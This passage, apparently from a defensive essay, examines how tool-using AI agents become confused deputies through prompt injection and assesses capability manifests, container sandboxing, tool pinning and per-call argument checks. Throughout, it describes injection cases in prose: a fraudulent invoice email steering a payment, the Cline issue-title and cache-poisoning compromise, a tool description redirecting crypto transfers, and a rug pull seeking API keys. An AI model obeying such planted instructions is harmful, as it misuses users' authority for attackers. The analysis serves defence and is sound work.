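# Capability manifests, session budgets and hardened output parsing as layered defences for AI agents that use tools

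## How an agent with tools becomes a confused deputy

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that acts on what the model writes. The software can send an email, query a database or pay a bill, and programmers call each such function a *tool*. Agents with tools now sort bug reports and answer correspondence, so they read a lot of text by people who have no authority over them. This exposes them to *prompt injection*, in which someone plants text in an email or a web page and the model obeys it as if the user had written it. The agent then uses its own permissions to do what the author of the text could not have done alone. Security engineers call such a program a *confused deputy*, a term decades older than language models. It means a program with legitimate authority that someone without that authority manages to misuse.

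### The agent loop

For example, an accounts assistant in a small company's finance office might have four tools: one to read a shared inbox, one to look up suppliers in the company's records, one to pay invoices and one to send replies. Each morning a clerk asks it to deal with the new invoices. The attacker can email the inbox, as anyone can, but cannot change the assistant's code or log in to the company's systems. The threat model in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) is broader, because it also includes malicious users and poisoned memory. Both models assume that the attacker works through what the agent reads.

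The assistant runs in a loop. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes this loop for Claude models, and other agents follow much the same pattern.

1. The *runtime*, the ordinary software around the model, sends the model the clerk's request and a list of the tools, with the arguments that each one expects.
2. The model answers with a structured request, for instance to read the inbox.
3. The runtime carries out that request and collects the result, here the text of the new emails.
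4. The runtime adds the result to the conversation so far and sends the whole of it back to the model.
5. The model asks for another tool, and the loop goes round again, or it writes a final answer and the loop ends.

Anthropic writes, "The model never runs anything on its own." The model's request to pay an invoice always passes through conventional software, which can block the payment.

Many agents get their tools from servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used standard. The runtime requests a list of tools from a server, forwards the model's chosen call to that server and returns the result to the model. MCP's *Tools* (2026) specification describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model can find and invoke them by itself, based on the user's prompt and the context. The specification recommends but does not require that a human always be able to deny a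 call.

### One channel for instructions and data

Siu and colleagues write the moment at which the model picks its next action as

*a*ₜ ~ *f*( · | *p*, *Tr*ₜ₋₁, *M*ₜ )

where *f* is the model, *p* is the user's request, *Tr*ₜ₋₁ is the record of all earlier actions with whatever came back from them, and *M*ₜ is any stored memory. The clerk's instruction is *p*. A stranger's email is somewhere inside *Tr*ₜ₋₁. The notation keeps the two apart, but the model receives them as one run of text.

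SQL injection is a related problem that older software has largely solved. An attacker types a database command into a web form, and a badly written site passes it to the database, which executes it. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the user's input to the database separately, so the input can never run as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C warns against expecting the same fix for prompt injection. A database engine is designed to treat commands and values differently, but a language model only predicts the next token (a fragment of text) from all the tokens before it, so there is no separate place to put the email.

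Developers do label the parts of the conversation, with tags that mark one stretch as the user's and another as a tool's output. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether those labels register inside the model. They wrapped identical passages in different tags and trained a classifier on the model's internal activations to recover the tag, so that the classifier could learn nothing except what the tags do. Then they took a conversation about gardening, put all of it inside user tags, and ran the classifier over it. The passages in the style of the model's private reasoning still registered as reasoning, with an average probability of 85%, against 2% for user text. A further comparison comes closer to the hostile email: text that sounded like a user, placed inside tool tags, registered as tool output with a probability of 20% at most. The labels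 have some effect, but style has a bigger one, and whoever writes the email chooses the style. (Taking a passage for the user's words is not yet obeying it, and models differ in how often they go that far.)

### The compiler that overwrote the bills

The term "confused deputy" comes from Hardy's 1988 paper *The Confused Deputy*, which describes an accident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a Fortran compiler in a system directory called SYSX, and customers who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The operators also wanted statistics on which language features people used, so they gave the compiler permission to write files in SYSX, where the statistics file was kept. The billing records, (SYSX)BILL, were in the same directory. One customer learned that filename and gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. The compiler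 passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the write because the compiler had permission for SYSX, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

Hardy considers the obvious repairs and finds a problem with each. The compiler could refuse to write into other people's directories, but customers had good reasons to want that. It could refuse names in SYSX, but some people had legitimate access there. A check for the name BILL would leave the other sensitive files exposed, and someone would have to extend it with every new file. The engineers did add a system call that let the compiler state whether it was using its own authority or the customer's, but they soon found applications that needed more than two authorities. Hardy concludes that the compiler "serves two masters", carries some authority from each, and has no way to keep the two apart. The code that wrote the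 debugging output was correct until the operators granted the compiler a licence for another purpose.

Gallo (2026), in *Proof-of-Continuity*, reduces the case to four conditions. Take a user *U*, a deputy *D*, and a privilege (*o*, *r*), meaning an operation *o* on a resource *r*. Then *D* is a confused deputy when

- (*o*, *r*) ∉ Priv(*U*): the user lacks the privilege;
- (*o*, *r*) ∈ Priv(*D*): the deputy has it;
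- *U* sends *D* a request;
- as a consequence, *D* carries out (*o*, *r*).

In the accounts assistant's version of the Tymshare case, the operation is paying instead of writing, and the resource is the company's bank account instead of the billing file. The attacker sends an email that looks like a supplier's reminder. Halfway down is an instruction for finance staff to pay the attached invoice today, to a new account number, and reply with the full supplier list for verification. When the assistant reads the inbox, the email enters the context, and the model's next output is a request to pay. The request is a well-formed call to a tool that the assistant may use, so the runtime executes it and the payment goes through.

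| Role | Tymshare's compiler | Accounts assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Deputy | The compiler | The model with its runtime |
| Party without the authority | The customer who typed the file name | The sender of the email |
| Owner of the authority | Tymshare's operators | The company, through its clerk |
| Authority open to misuse | Licence to write in SYSX | Permission to pay and to send mail |
| What carries the request | A file name | Sentences in the body of an email |

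An agent is in a worse position than Tymshare's compiler, because an attacker can try to choose the operation as well as the target. Tymshare's customer could choose only where the compiler wrote its debugging output. The sender of an email can try to choose any of the assistant's tools, along with every argument. David C therefore calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". In this view, engineers can repair a classical confused deputy, but can only reduce the likelihood and impact of confusion in a model. In the same post, David C measures impact by assuming that the attacker has direct access to the tools and asking what the worst outcome would be.

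### Two uses of the term

Writers on agents apply "confused deputy" to two situations that need different fixes. In one, the user lacks permission for what they ask the agent to do. The security firm Quarkslab built a mock medical assistant whose lookup tool could fetch any patient's record. A logged-in patient asked for the history of patient number 2 and got it. A stricter system prompt (the developer's standing instructions to the model) stopped the plain request, but not the same request hidden in a comment inside a web page that the patient supplied. Quarkslab fixed the problem by changing the tool to take the patient's number from the login session, where the model could not alter it.

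In the other use, the user is fully authorised and an outsider exploits that authority. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) describes prompt injection as untrusted content that borrows the authority of the human user. The paper notes that an inbox is hard to secure because the agent needs permission to read it and the adversary's instructions also arrive there. The accounts assistant has this second problem, which Quarkslab's repair would not fix. The clerk is logged in and allowed to pay invoices, so every identity check gives the correct result even though the attacker instigated the payment.

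(The Model Context Protocol's security guidance uses the term more narrowly again, for a flaw in servers that log in to other services on a user's behalf, by which an attacker can skip the consent screen.)

Forbidding an accounts assistant to follow any instruction it finds in an email would be useless, because an honest invoice is itself a request to pay a certain sum into a certain account, and the clerk wants the assistant to act on it. The definition in Siu and colleagues allows for this. An indirect prompt injection, which arrives through content, occurs when the agent follows instructions from an unauthorised source *and* the resulting action does not serve the user's task. The second condition is the hard one for software to apply, since it depends on what the clerk meant.

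### Two senses of "capability"

Hardy's subtitle was "or why capabilities might have been invented", but a "capability manifest" usually has little to do with the capabilities Hardy meant.

In the looser sense, a capability is an entry in a permission list. Permissions can be laid out in a table with a row for each program, a column for each resource, and cells listing the operations that the program may perform on the resource. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) describes how textbooks came to treat a capability system as this table read by row, and an access control list as the table read by column. On that reading, the two hold the same information.

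Miller and colleagues reject the equivalence because the table leaves out how a program refers to a resource. In Hardy's sense, a capability is a reference that both picks out a resource and carries the right to use it. A program cannot make one up and has to receive it from someone who already holds it. Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) illustrates the difference with a word processor. Today the user picks a document, the operating system gives the program the document's name as a string, and the program can substitute any other name and open whatever the user could open. The essay calls this *ambient authority*, permission that a program can use for any purpose. With capabilities, the program starts with access to nothing, and the user's choice of a document gives it an open handle to that one file. Tymshare's compiler would have received a reference to the statistics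 file from the operators and another to the output file from the customer. A customer with no right to the billing file could not have given the compiler a reference to it.

Most manifests for agent tools are capability lists in the first sense. An entry might allow the assistant to call the payment tool, but the account number arrives separately, as a string that the model wrote and quite possibly copied from an email. Naming the payee is again separate from having the right to pay, and the same separation led to the loss of the billing records. MCP confusingly uses "capability" in two ways. In its specification, a server declares a "capability" when it supports a feature, such as offering tools. Its advice on identifiers such as a shopping-basket number uses the word as Hardy did. Model Context Protocol warns that on a server with logins, such a handle "is a name, not a capability", and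 that the server should check the caller's rights every time the handle is used.

Real object capabilities would reduce the accounts assistant's exposure but not eliminate it. If the assistant held an unforgeable payment reference for each approved supplier, it could not pay the attacker's new account, because it would have no reference to that account. But an email could still lead the model to pay a genuine supplier twice. Gallo makes the general point that capabilities rule out the classical confusion within a single step, but that it can return when a program holds a capability and uses it outside the request it came with.

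### The Cline compromise

In February 2026 the maintainers of Cline, an open-source AI coding assistant with about five million installs, lost control of one of their release channels for eight hours. The attack came through the title of a bug report. Adnan Khan, the security researcher who found the weakness, published it in *Clinejection* (adnanthekhan, 2026).

On 21 December 2025 the maintainers had added an AI agent to sort new GitHub issues (public bug reports). Anyone with a GitHub account could trigger it by opening an issue. The agent's tools included Bash, which runs any command on the machine, and the workflow pasted the issue's title straight into the agent's prompt. Khan showed that a title written to look like an error message could get the agent to install a "helper" package, which could run the attacker's code during installation. The attack worked on every attempt in a copy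 of the repository.

The agent could not publish anything itself. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) reports that the agent's GitHub permissions covered reading the code and writing to issues. But the agent shared a cache with the release process, a store of files that automated jobs reuse to save time. An attacker could fill the cache with more than ten gigabytes of junk, causing GitHub to delete the genuine files, and then add doctored ones under the same names. The nightly release job would then run the doctored files, giving them access to the publishing credentials.

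Khan reported this privately on 1 January and heard nothing. After he went public on 9 February, the maintainers removed the workflow within half an hour and began replacing credentials. But they deleted the wrong token for npm, the registry from which developers install JavaScript packages. On 17 February someone used the token that still worked to publish a version of Cline's command-line program that also installed OpenClaw, a separate AI agent. The package had about 4,000 downloads before it was removed, according to a blog quoted in LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026).

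Khan had thought the issue-sorting agent was the most obvious way in, but wasn't sure. Bargury (2026), in *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, later recovered the deleted issue from a public archive. Someone had opened it on 28 January with a title copied from Khan's publicly visible test material, then renamed it "user error" five minutes later. The script that the package fetched is gone, so the middle of the reconstruction is missing, though the rest fits closely. The official advisory, OSV's *GHSA-9ppg-jx86-fqw7* (2026), rates the severity as low because OpenClaw is a legitimate program and nothing else in the package had changed. Bargury thinks the rating is absurd. That view is more convincing, because the intruder chose the harmless payload and could have used the stolen token to publish a harmful one just as easily.

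All of Gallo's conditions are present. A stranger with a GitHub account had no right to run code in Cline's workflows, but the agent did, and the stranger's issue title made the agent use that right. Cline concedes this, comparing the arrangement to giving every GitHub user shell access. The agent's formal permissions looked modest, but its real reach came from a general-purpose tool and a shared cache. Someone reading the permission list would have had to know about both to see what the agent could do.

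### Least privilege, and where it runs out

Khan proposed, among other fixes, removing Bash and the file-editing tools so that the agent kept only what it needs to sort issues. This follows the principle of *least privilege*, which holds that a program should have no more authority than its job needs. David C relays a stricter version for language models, in which a model should drop to a party's privileges when it processes that party's text.

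Either rule would have kept the stranger away from the release process when the agent's job was sorting bug reports. The accounts assistant is harder to protect because its job is to read mail from strangers and pay invoices based on it. Under the stricter rule it could never pay anyone, and under the ordinary rule it keeps exactly the permissions that the attacker wants. The remaining option is to limit how it uses those permissions, with controls in the software outside the model that keep working even when the model is following the attacker's instructions. A *capability manifest* is a machine-readable declaration of the resources each tool may use and the effects it may have, which the runtime can check each call against. A *session budget* is a limit, enforced by the runtime, on what the assistant may spend, use up or send out in one continuous run. *Hardened output parsing* reduces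 a tool's result to expected fields, types and ranges before any of it reaches the model.

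## Declaring what each tool may do

Android apps have long come with a manifest that names the permissions they need, such as the camera or the internet. MCP servers usually come with nothing similar, and many of them run as ordinary programs on the user's machine with all of the user's privileges. For the accounts assistant, a manifest might look like this:

```yaml
default:                  # holds unless a tool's own entry differs
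  files: none
  hosts: none
  secrets: none
  commands: none

read_inbox:
  hosts: [mail-server]
  secrets: [MAIL_READ_TOKEN]
  effects: [read the invoices mailbox]

look_up_supplier:
  files: [read suppliers.db]
  effects: [read supplier records]

pay_invoice:
  hosts: [bank-gateway]
  secrets: [BANK_PAYMENT_TOKEN]
  effects: [move money out of the company account]

send_reply:
  hosts: [mail-server]
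  secrets: [MAIL_SEND_TOKEN]
  effects: [send text to an outside address]
```

### The five fields

The `files` field lists the paths a tool may use and what it may do at each. The supplier lookup can read one database and cannot write to any files. Even if an attacker managed to run code inside that tool, the code could not replace a supplier's account number with the attacker's own.

The `hosts` field names the machines that a tool may contact. Limits on files and on the network are each weak alone, as Anthropic explains in describing the *sandbox* for its coding agent, Claude Code. A sandbox is a boundary that the operating system enforces around a running program. Without network limits, a hijacked agent could send out files such as SSH keys, which log a user in to other machines. It could also escape the sandbox and gain network access if its file access were not limited.

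The `secrets` field covers passwords and access tokens. Programs often receive these as environment variables, which are named values, and by default a program inherits all of them when it starts. In the accounts assistant, both mail tools connect to the same machine, so a firewall treats them alike and only their tokens differ. Separate tokens help only if the mail provider issues tokens that can read but not send. McKerchar's *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security firm Sophos, recommends keeping the most sensitive credentials out of the agent's process. The agent then supplies only a tool's name and parameters, and a separate process adds the credential, makes the call and returns the parsed response.

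The `commands` field needs the most care, because a tool that can run any command can often bypass the other limits, as happened with Bash at Cline. A reviewer also learns very little from an entry for command execution. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) describes MCP servers that operate a connected phone through a developer's command-line program, for instance to make calls. Its scheme correctly labels such a server "execute commands", so the manifest would not mention phones or calls.

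The operating system can enforce those four fields, but not `effects`. Checking the balance and emptying the account both use an encrypted connection to the bank gateway, which the operating system can't read, so either the tool or the runtime has to distinguish them.

### Per server, per tool or per effect

If one vendor supplies all four of the assistant's tools in a single MCP server, a manifest for the whole server has to cover everything any of them needs: the mail server, the bank gateway, the supplier database and all three tokens. An attacker who exploited a bug in the supplier lookup could then reach the bank, even though that tool never needs the bank.

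Declaring permissions per tool closes that route but takes some engineering work. Operating systems place limits on processes, and the tools of an MCP server normally share one process, so an operator who wants separate limits for each tool may have to split the server into several.

Many existing servers don't separate their tools or their callers. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (Huang, Dai and colleagues, 2026) analysed 6,137 MCP servers and found insecure authorisation in 2,846 of them (46.4%). Some never checked who was calling, while others checked once, stored the result and accepted later calls from anyone. If the accounts server worked like this, another program on the same network might be able to call the payment tool without involving the assistant. A manifest that treats the server as one trusted unit would also permit that call.

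Even a per-tool entry for `pay_invoice` does not specify who may receive the money. Wei and Xiong (2026) make the same criticism of permissions to send mail in *Access Control for Agentic AI*, since these do not specify which mail may be sent. They propose declaring authority as a set of effects for one task: what the agent may read, what it may disclose and to whom, what it may change, and how much it may spend. The entry might then permit the assistant to pay open invoices from approved suppliers into the accounts on file. That would block payment to the attacker's new account, but not payment of a duplicate invoice that the records listed as open.

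Enforcing such an entry means checking the argument values of each call, and someone has to know what every tool actually does. Wei and Xiong prove that their checks are sound if the declared effects are true, but they have not measured a working system. McKerchar describes a more modest version, in which each sensitive tool has a fixed request format and its own list of permitted hosts. Every integration needs a definition, so the agent cannot improvise with unfamiliar services. McKerchar found no project that offers the whole arrangement.

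### How AgentBound works

AgentBound declares permissions for each server. It has a manifest format, a generator that drafts manifests from a server's source code, and an engine that runs the server inside a *container*, an isolated environment with its own view of the files and network.

The capability vocabulary is based on Android's permissions. Bühler and colleagues collected 16 uses of AI agents from eleven papers, ranging from route planning to legal drafting, and matched each action involved to the nearest Android permission. Because MCP servers mostly run on desktop computers, they then compared the result with macOS's permission system and dropped phone-only permissions, such as body sensors. They merged similar permissions, such as precise and approximate location, then added environment variables, control of other processes and the clipboard. The final list has 18 capabilities,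 none of which concerns payments or email.

A manifest in this vocabulary declares general kinds of permission. For the accounts server, these would be reading files, reading environment variables and opening outgoing connections. When the agent first starts the server, the engine narrows each permission to something specific, such as read-only access to one directory or a connection to one web address, and asks the user to approve it. If the agent requests a kind of permission that the manifest lacks, the engine aborts. A developer whose server contacts only one service can write that service's address into the manifest.

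The engine enforces the result in three ways:

- For files, it mounts only the approved directories in the container, so the server has no path to any others.
- For secrets, it passes in only the approved environment variables.
- For the network, a start-up script looks up the numerical addresses of the permitted hosts, adds them to the container's firewall and blocks all other traffic.

The model plays no part in enforcing these limits, so an email can't open the firewall by manipulating the model. The limits still depend on the underlying software, and an attacker who could exploit a flaw in Docker, the program that runs the containers, could bypass them.

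The start-up order leaves another gap. The script needs the network to install the server's package from a public registry, so it closes the firewall only afterwards. Packages can run code during installation, and Khan's proposed attack on Cline relied on this. A malicious package could therefore send out any files or tokens already in the container before the firewall closes. Operators could avoid this by building the container beforehand, without any secrets in it.

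### How accurate the manifests are

Bühler and colleagues ran the generator on 296 of the most popular MCP servers on GitHub. A small model, GPT-5 mini, read each server's code and documentation and drafted five manifests, which the larger GPT-5 then merged. Of the resulting manifests, 83.1% declared outgoing network access, 79.6% environment variables and 74.1% reading files. Because most servers need these three permissions, the general manifest does little to distinguish an honest server from one that steals data, and that check has to rely on the concrete paths and hosts.

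The team then asked the maintainers of 96 servers whether the manifests for their servers were correct. About 74% of the maintainers did not reply. The paper's headline accuracy of 80.9% rests on only 21 verdicts, of which 17 accepted the manifest and four rejected it. Four more cases were still under discussion. One maintainer objected that the server only called online services and did not need to read files. Another wanted access to specific environment variables instead of all of them, though the engine would have asked the user about these at run time.

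The paper also reports that the manifests were complete (100% recall) because no maintainer mentioned a missing capability, but a comparison with handwritten manifests casts doubt on this. Two authors wrote manifests for 48 of the same servers, 24 each, and compared them with the generated ones. In 23 of the 29 mismatches they found, the generator had left out something that the human had included.

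The two sets agreed on 787 of 816 entries, or 96.4%. This figure is inflated because an entry also counts as a match when both manifests omit a capability. The comparison covered 17 capabilities per server (presumably with writing and deleting merged), and the frequencies above suggest that a typical server needs three or four of them, so a blank manifest would agree on about 80% of the entries. A fairer summary is that 28 of the 48 manifests were identical to the human version and 20 contained at least one mismatch. The paper's recall of 0.96 for this comparison is also hard to reconcile with 23 omissions, since it would imply more than eleven correctly declared capabilities per server.

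Only six of the 29 mismatches were unnecessary entries, which is reassuring for security because an unnecessary entry leaves the server with a permission that an attacker might use. An omission instead stops part of the server from working until someone corrects the manifest. The generator therefore looks useful for producing a first draft that someone who knows the server then corrects, as its designers intend.

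Running a server in the container adds little delay. Over 1,000 runs of common operations, such as reading a file or fetching a web page, the container added an average of 0.6 milliseconds on a Mac and 0.29 on Debian Linux. Starting a server took about 90 to 430 milliseconds longer, not counting package installation. A server usually starts once and then handles many calls, so users are unlikely to notice either delay.

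### Which attacks it stopped

Bühler and colleagues first wrote a server that tries to steal an SSH key. Outside a container, the server sent the key out. In a container with network access blocked, it could read the key but not send it. When the container also restricted file access, the server could not read the key.

They then tried 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections. AgentBound stopped the attacks on eight of them, stopped some of the attacks in a ninth, and failed against five.

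| Attack | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Maps and weather servers switch to an attacker's address while running (2 servers) | Stopped | The firewall does not list the new address |
| Tool descriptions or injected prompts lead to forbidden files or other system resources (4 servers) | Stopped | The container lacks access to those resources |
| Flaws in a server's own code expose files or a command shell (2 servers) | Stopped | The engine limits access to both |
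| One server combines several attacks | Partly stopped | Some of them only manipulate the model's output |
| Injected prompts affect only the model (2 servers) | Not stopped | The server does nothing outside its manifest |
| A flaw in a server's code touches no system resource | Not stopped | There is no forbidden access to block |
| A time server's description redirects cryptocurrency transfers | Not stopped | The wallet tool is allowed to make transfers |
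| A database command hides in ordinary input (SQL injection) | Not stopped | The server needs its database |

The time server is the case closest to the accounts assistant. Its tool only reported the time, but its description included an instruction to send cryptocurrency transfers through a "privacy proxy" whenever the model used a separate wallet tool. The description entered the model's context along with every other tool's, and the model could then pass the attacker's address to the wallet. The time server didn't need network access for this. The wallet tool made a transfer that its own permissions allowed, and only the recipient was wrong. For the same reason, the container would not stop an email that changes the account number on an invoice.

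In the SQL injection, the attacker's text runs as a command on a database that the server is authorized to use. The container could block the server's access to other databases, but it can't distinguish legitimate queries from malicious ones, so the flaw should be fixed in the server's code.

Fourteen servers are too few to yield a meaningful success rate, and ten of them come from a set of deliberately vulnerable servers built for security practice. The tests also relied on honest manifests. For the maps, weather, time and database servers, the team used manifests generated from the original, harmless versions. The team wrote the other ten manifests, and one member approved the concrete permissions. The experiment therefore supports only the claim that a correct manifest confines a hostile server to its declared resources.

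### Who writes the manifest

Bühler and colleagues expect developers to distribute a manifest with each server. A developer knows best what the server needs, but a malicious developer can request every permission, and an honest one in a hurry may do the same. The manifest is therefore only a request for permissions until someone with no stake in the server approves it.

Generating a second manifest from the source code lets the operator compare it with the first. However, the generator is an agent that reads untrusted text, and an attacker could add a code comment claiming that a calculator needs network access. The generator rejects capabilities outside the fixed vocabulary, which limits what such a comment could achieve, but this check would not block the calculator example because `mcp.ac.network.client` is in the vocabulary.

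McKerchar suggests treating manifests like program code. An agent that needs a new service may draft the manifest, automated tests check its format and the tool's behaviour, and a human reviewer decides whether to accept it, so the agent cannot widen its own permissions. Review can take hours, which seems acceptable for a payment tool that rarely changes.

Approval loses its value if the tool changes afterwards. In a *rug pull*, a server behaves well until people trust it, and then its operator changes a tool's description. One server in the AgentBound tests offered a weather forecast, then changed its description after the third call to tell the model to look for API keys in a configuration file. The limits on file access stopped this attack, but they would not have stopped a new description that told the model to redirect a payment.

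The Model Context Protocol (MCP) allows tool lists to change over time. Its specification recommends that servers supporting change notices send them to subscribed clients, but does not require it, and an attacker has no reason to comply. A runtime also cannot rely on having inspected the server when it first connected. The July 2026 version removed the opening handshake and protocol-level sessions, so each request is independent and may reach a different copy of the server (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

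The runtime can protect itself by *pinning*. When the operator approves a tool, the runtime stores a cryptographic hash (a short fingerprint) of the tool's name, description and input format. It recomputes the hash whenever it fetches the tool list again, and withholds the tool if the hash has changed. The specification makes this easier by forbidding servers from varying their tool lists between connections, although the lists may depend on the caller's credentials.

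Pinning a description does not pin the code behind it. Wei and Xiong point out that a tool's behaviour can change while its interface stays the same, and they want its declared effects checked again with every new version. For a package that runs locally, the operator can fix the exact version and its hash. If the server runs on someone else's machine, the operator cannot inspect the code and can only limit what the server receives. A pin preserves whatever the operator approved, so it would not have helped if the time server's description had been hostile from the start.

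A digital signature shows who published a manifest and whether anyone has altered it since, so it would expose tampering on the way from the developer to the user. It would not show that the manifest is accurate, and an attacker who took over a developer's release process, as Khan showed was possible at Cline, might be able to sign manifests too.

### MCP's tool annotations

The protocol does have a place to describe side effects. Since March 2025, the author of a tool has been able to attach four optional labels, or *annotations*:

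- `readOnlyHint`: the tool changes nothing (default: false).
- `destructiveHint`: its changes may destroy something, as opposed to only adding to it (default: true).
- `idempotentHint`: repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect (default: false).
- `openWorldHint`: the tool deals with outside parties or systems (default: true).

The default labels describe the worst case, so labelling adds little information about the tools that matter most. An honest author would probably mark `pay_invoice` as able to change things, destructive, unsafe to repeat and open to the outside world, but a tool with no labels gets the same values. The labels also don't distinguish paying a bill from deleting a folder on a remote server.

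The larger difficulty is whether clients can trust the annotations. During the original discussion, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, asked how a client could use an annotation it cannot trust. The specification ended up calling all annotations hints, and the current version requires clients to treat them as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server. In a March blog post, the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) warn that a server's author can mark a tool as read-only and have it delete files anyway, and that anyone who needs a guarantee should use network controls or a sandbox.

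Annotations are still useful. A runtime can accept an untrusted server's label that a tool is destructive with little risk, because the worst result is an unnecessary confirmation prompt. It should not accept the same server's label that a tool is harmless. A company that runs its own MCP servers can also enforce rules based on the labels, such as blocking tools that contact outsiders once the agent has read private data. Few people seem to do anything like this yet. The nearest example the maintainers give is GitHub's read-only mode, which about 17% of its users have switched on.

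Several proposals would add to the set of labels that describe tools. One, from engineers at GitHub and OpenAI, would add labels for trust and sensitivity, and another would add labels for corporate governance. The Model Context Protocol group working on annotations lists both as drafts on its page and has not decided whether a few simple hints are better than a richer set. A new label for payments would still depend on the honesty of whoever attached it.

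### What agent products enforce by default

OpenAI's Codex has stricter defaults than the other best-known coding agents. According to OpenAI, when Codex runs on a user's machine, the operating system enforces a sandbox that usually confines it to the current project folder and blocks network access. OpenAI's *Permissions* describes profiles for the local commands Codex runs. These profiles resemble manifests, with one set of rules for files and another for network destinations. A profile can also deny access to particular files, such as those that hold passwords, while allowing work on the rest of the project. For its own staff, OpenAI makes the sandbox compulsory, permits expected network destinations and requires approval for unfamiliar ones.

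Claude Code has a sandbox too, but Anthropic's documentation states that it is off by default. When turned on, it covers shell commands and the processes they start, but not Claude's file tools, MCP servers or hooks (scripts that run automatically at set moments). On Windows, commands run without the sandbox unless the user installs a Linux environment. If the sandbox is turned on but cannot start, for example because a component is missing, Claude Code by default shows a warning and runs the commands anyway. A setting turns this into a hard failure, which would be the better choice on any unattended machine.

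OpenClaw, the agent that the intruder installed through Cline's package, can run its tools in Docker containers, but McKerchar notes that users have to opt in. According to OpenClaw's own documentation, the containers are not a perfect boundary.

These defaults mainly protect a developer's computer from a coding agent's commands. The accounts assistant runs no shell commands, and its payment tool would be an MCP server, which Claude Code's sandbox does not cover, so whoever builds the assistant has to isolate that server. Anthropic offers a separate sandbox program that can wrap a standalone MCP server, and OpenAI's *Sandbox security* advises developers to use isolated machines and allow outgoing traffic only to approved addresses. In either case, someone at the company must specify that the payment tool may contact only the bank.

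## Checking the arguments of every call

In a *per-call check*, ordinary code in the runtime compares a call's argument values with rules that the operator wrote, before the call takes effect. A manifest that allows `pay_invoice` does not restrict who may be paid, and the tool's schema might require only that an account number have a certain length. Without a per-call check, the model in effect decides which accounts may be paid.

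### ScopeGate's decision procedure

Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, describes a small checker called ScopeGate. It sits between the model and the tools, and its inputs are the proposed call, the operator's policy and some context from the runtime. It applies these steps in order:

1. Deny the call if the policy does not list the tool.
2. Deny it if the policy gives an argument a set of allowed values and the call's value is not in the set.
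3. For a tool that moves money, deny the call unless the amount is a finite number between zero and a ceiling.
4. Deny it if the tool needs an *idempotency key* and the runtime has not supplied one. The key is a label for one intended action, and the receiving service can use it to recognise a repeated request.
5. Allow a call that has passed every step. Any error along the way counts as a denial.

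Suppose the company's policy for `pay_invoice` lists approved suppliers' accounts, sets a limit of £5,000 and requires a key. The assistant reads one genuine invoice and one malicious email, and the model proposes a payment for each.

| Step | £1,200 to a supplier's account on file | £1,950 to the attacker's account |
|---|---|---|
| Is the tool in the policy? | Yes | Yes |
| Is the account in the allowed set? | Yes | No, so deny |
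| Is the amount finite and under the ceiling? | Yes | Not reached |
| Is there an idempotency key? | Yes | Not reached |
| Outcome | The bank receives the payment | The tool never runs |

Even if the fraudulent email gets the model to attempt the payment, the payment fails because the email cannot change the list of approved accounts. The check also blocks payments to a genuine supplier who has just changed banks, until someone at the company updates the list.

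The procedure still allows some harmful payments. An attacker could use an email to inflate a real supplier's bill from £490 to £4,900, which is still under the ceiling, or to request a second payment of the same invoice. ScopeGate checks only that a key exists, so the bank will catch the duplicate only if the runtime gives both payments the same key, for instance by deriving it from the invoice number. Many small payments would also pass unless a session budget limits their total. The other half of the attack, replying with the supplier list, is even harder to block with a set of allowed values, because the body of a reply is free text and the assistant has good reason to answer whoever wrote in.

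### Keeping the policy out of the model's reach

An injection can change the account number that the model proposes. If the model also supplied or extended the list of approved accounts, the same injection could change that list too, and the check would compare one attacker-chosen value with another. Mellafe Zuvic therefore rules out model output as a direct or indirect source for any part of the policy, whether when the policy is written, at the start of a session or during an update.

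An accounts assistant that copied new bank details from emails into the supplier database would indirectly defeat ScopeGate if the approved accounts came from that database. The assistant's manifest prevents this by listing `suppliers.db` as read-only. In *Agenra* (2026), which describes a language for such policies, the agent can likewise request a call but cannot change the policy, register trusted values or issue approvals.

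Taken literally, the rule forbids the common convenience of having a language model draft the policy. Amazon's cloud business sells a per-call check that runs at a gateway outside the agent's code. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026), customers can describe a policy in ordinary language and have the service convert it into Cedar, a formal policy language. The conversion presumably uses a language model. This seems acceptable if that model reads only the operator's description and a person checks the result, since a stranger's email then cannot influence the policy. The remaining danger is an ordinary mistake. AWS analyses each set of policies for conflicts and redundant rules before the gateway accepts it, but this analysis cannot detect that the company meant to cap payments and forgot. *Agenra* makes the general point that a monitor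 cannot enforce a rule that is missing from its policy.

### What agent frameworks check by default

Many developers build agents on a framework that supplies the agent loop. Mellafe Zuvic read the public code of LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and Stripe's toolkit for payment agents, each at a fixed version. The audit found no code in any of the three that, by default, checks the concrete argument values after the model proposes a call and before the tool runs, and denies the call if the check fails.

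LangChain looks up the tool by name, validates the shape of the input in common cases, and runs the tool. Developers can attach callbacks that observe the call, but a callback's return value does not reliably stop it. They can also add a human approval step, which is off by default. LlamaIndex checks that the named tool exists and passes on whatever arguments the model wrote. If the tool does not exist, the model gets an error message, but the framework raises no security alert.

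Bad arguments could do the most harm in Stripe's toolkit, which handles payments. Developers can choose which actions to expose, and Stripe's restricted keys limit what the toolkit can do with an account. Within those limits, the toolkit forwards the amount, currency and customer that the model chooses. Stripe also runs a remote MCP server, which may perform further checks that outsiders cannot see.

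These are design choices rather than vulnerabilities in the usual sense, because the frameworks leave authorisation to the developer. A developer who doesn't know this could easily mistake a list of permitted tools for a complete permission system.

### Testing ScopeGate

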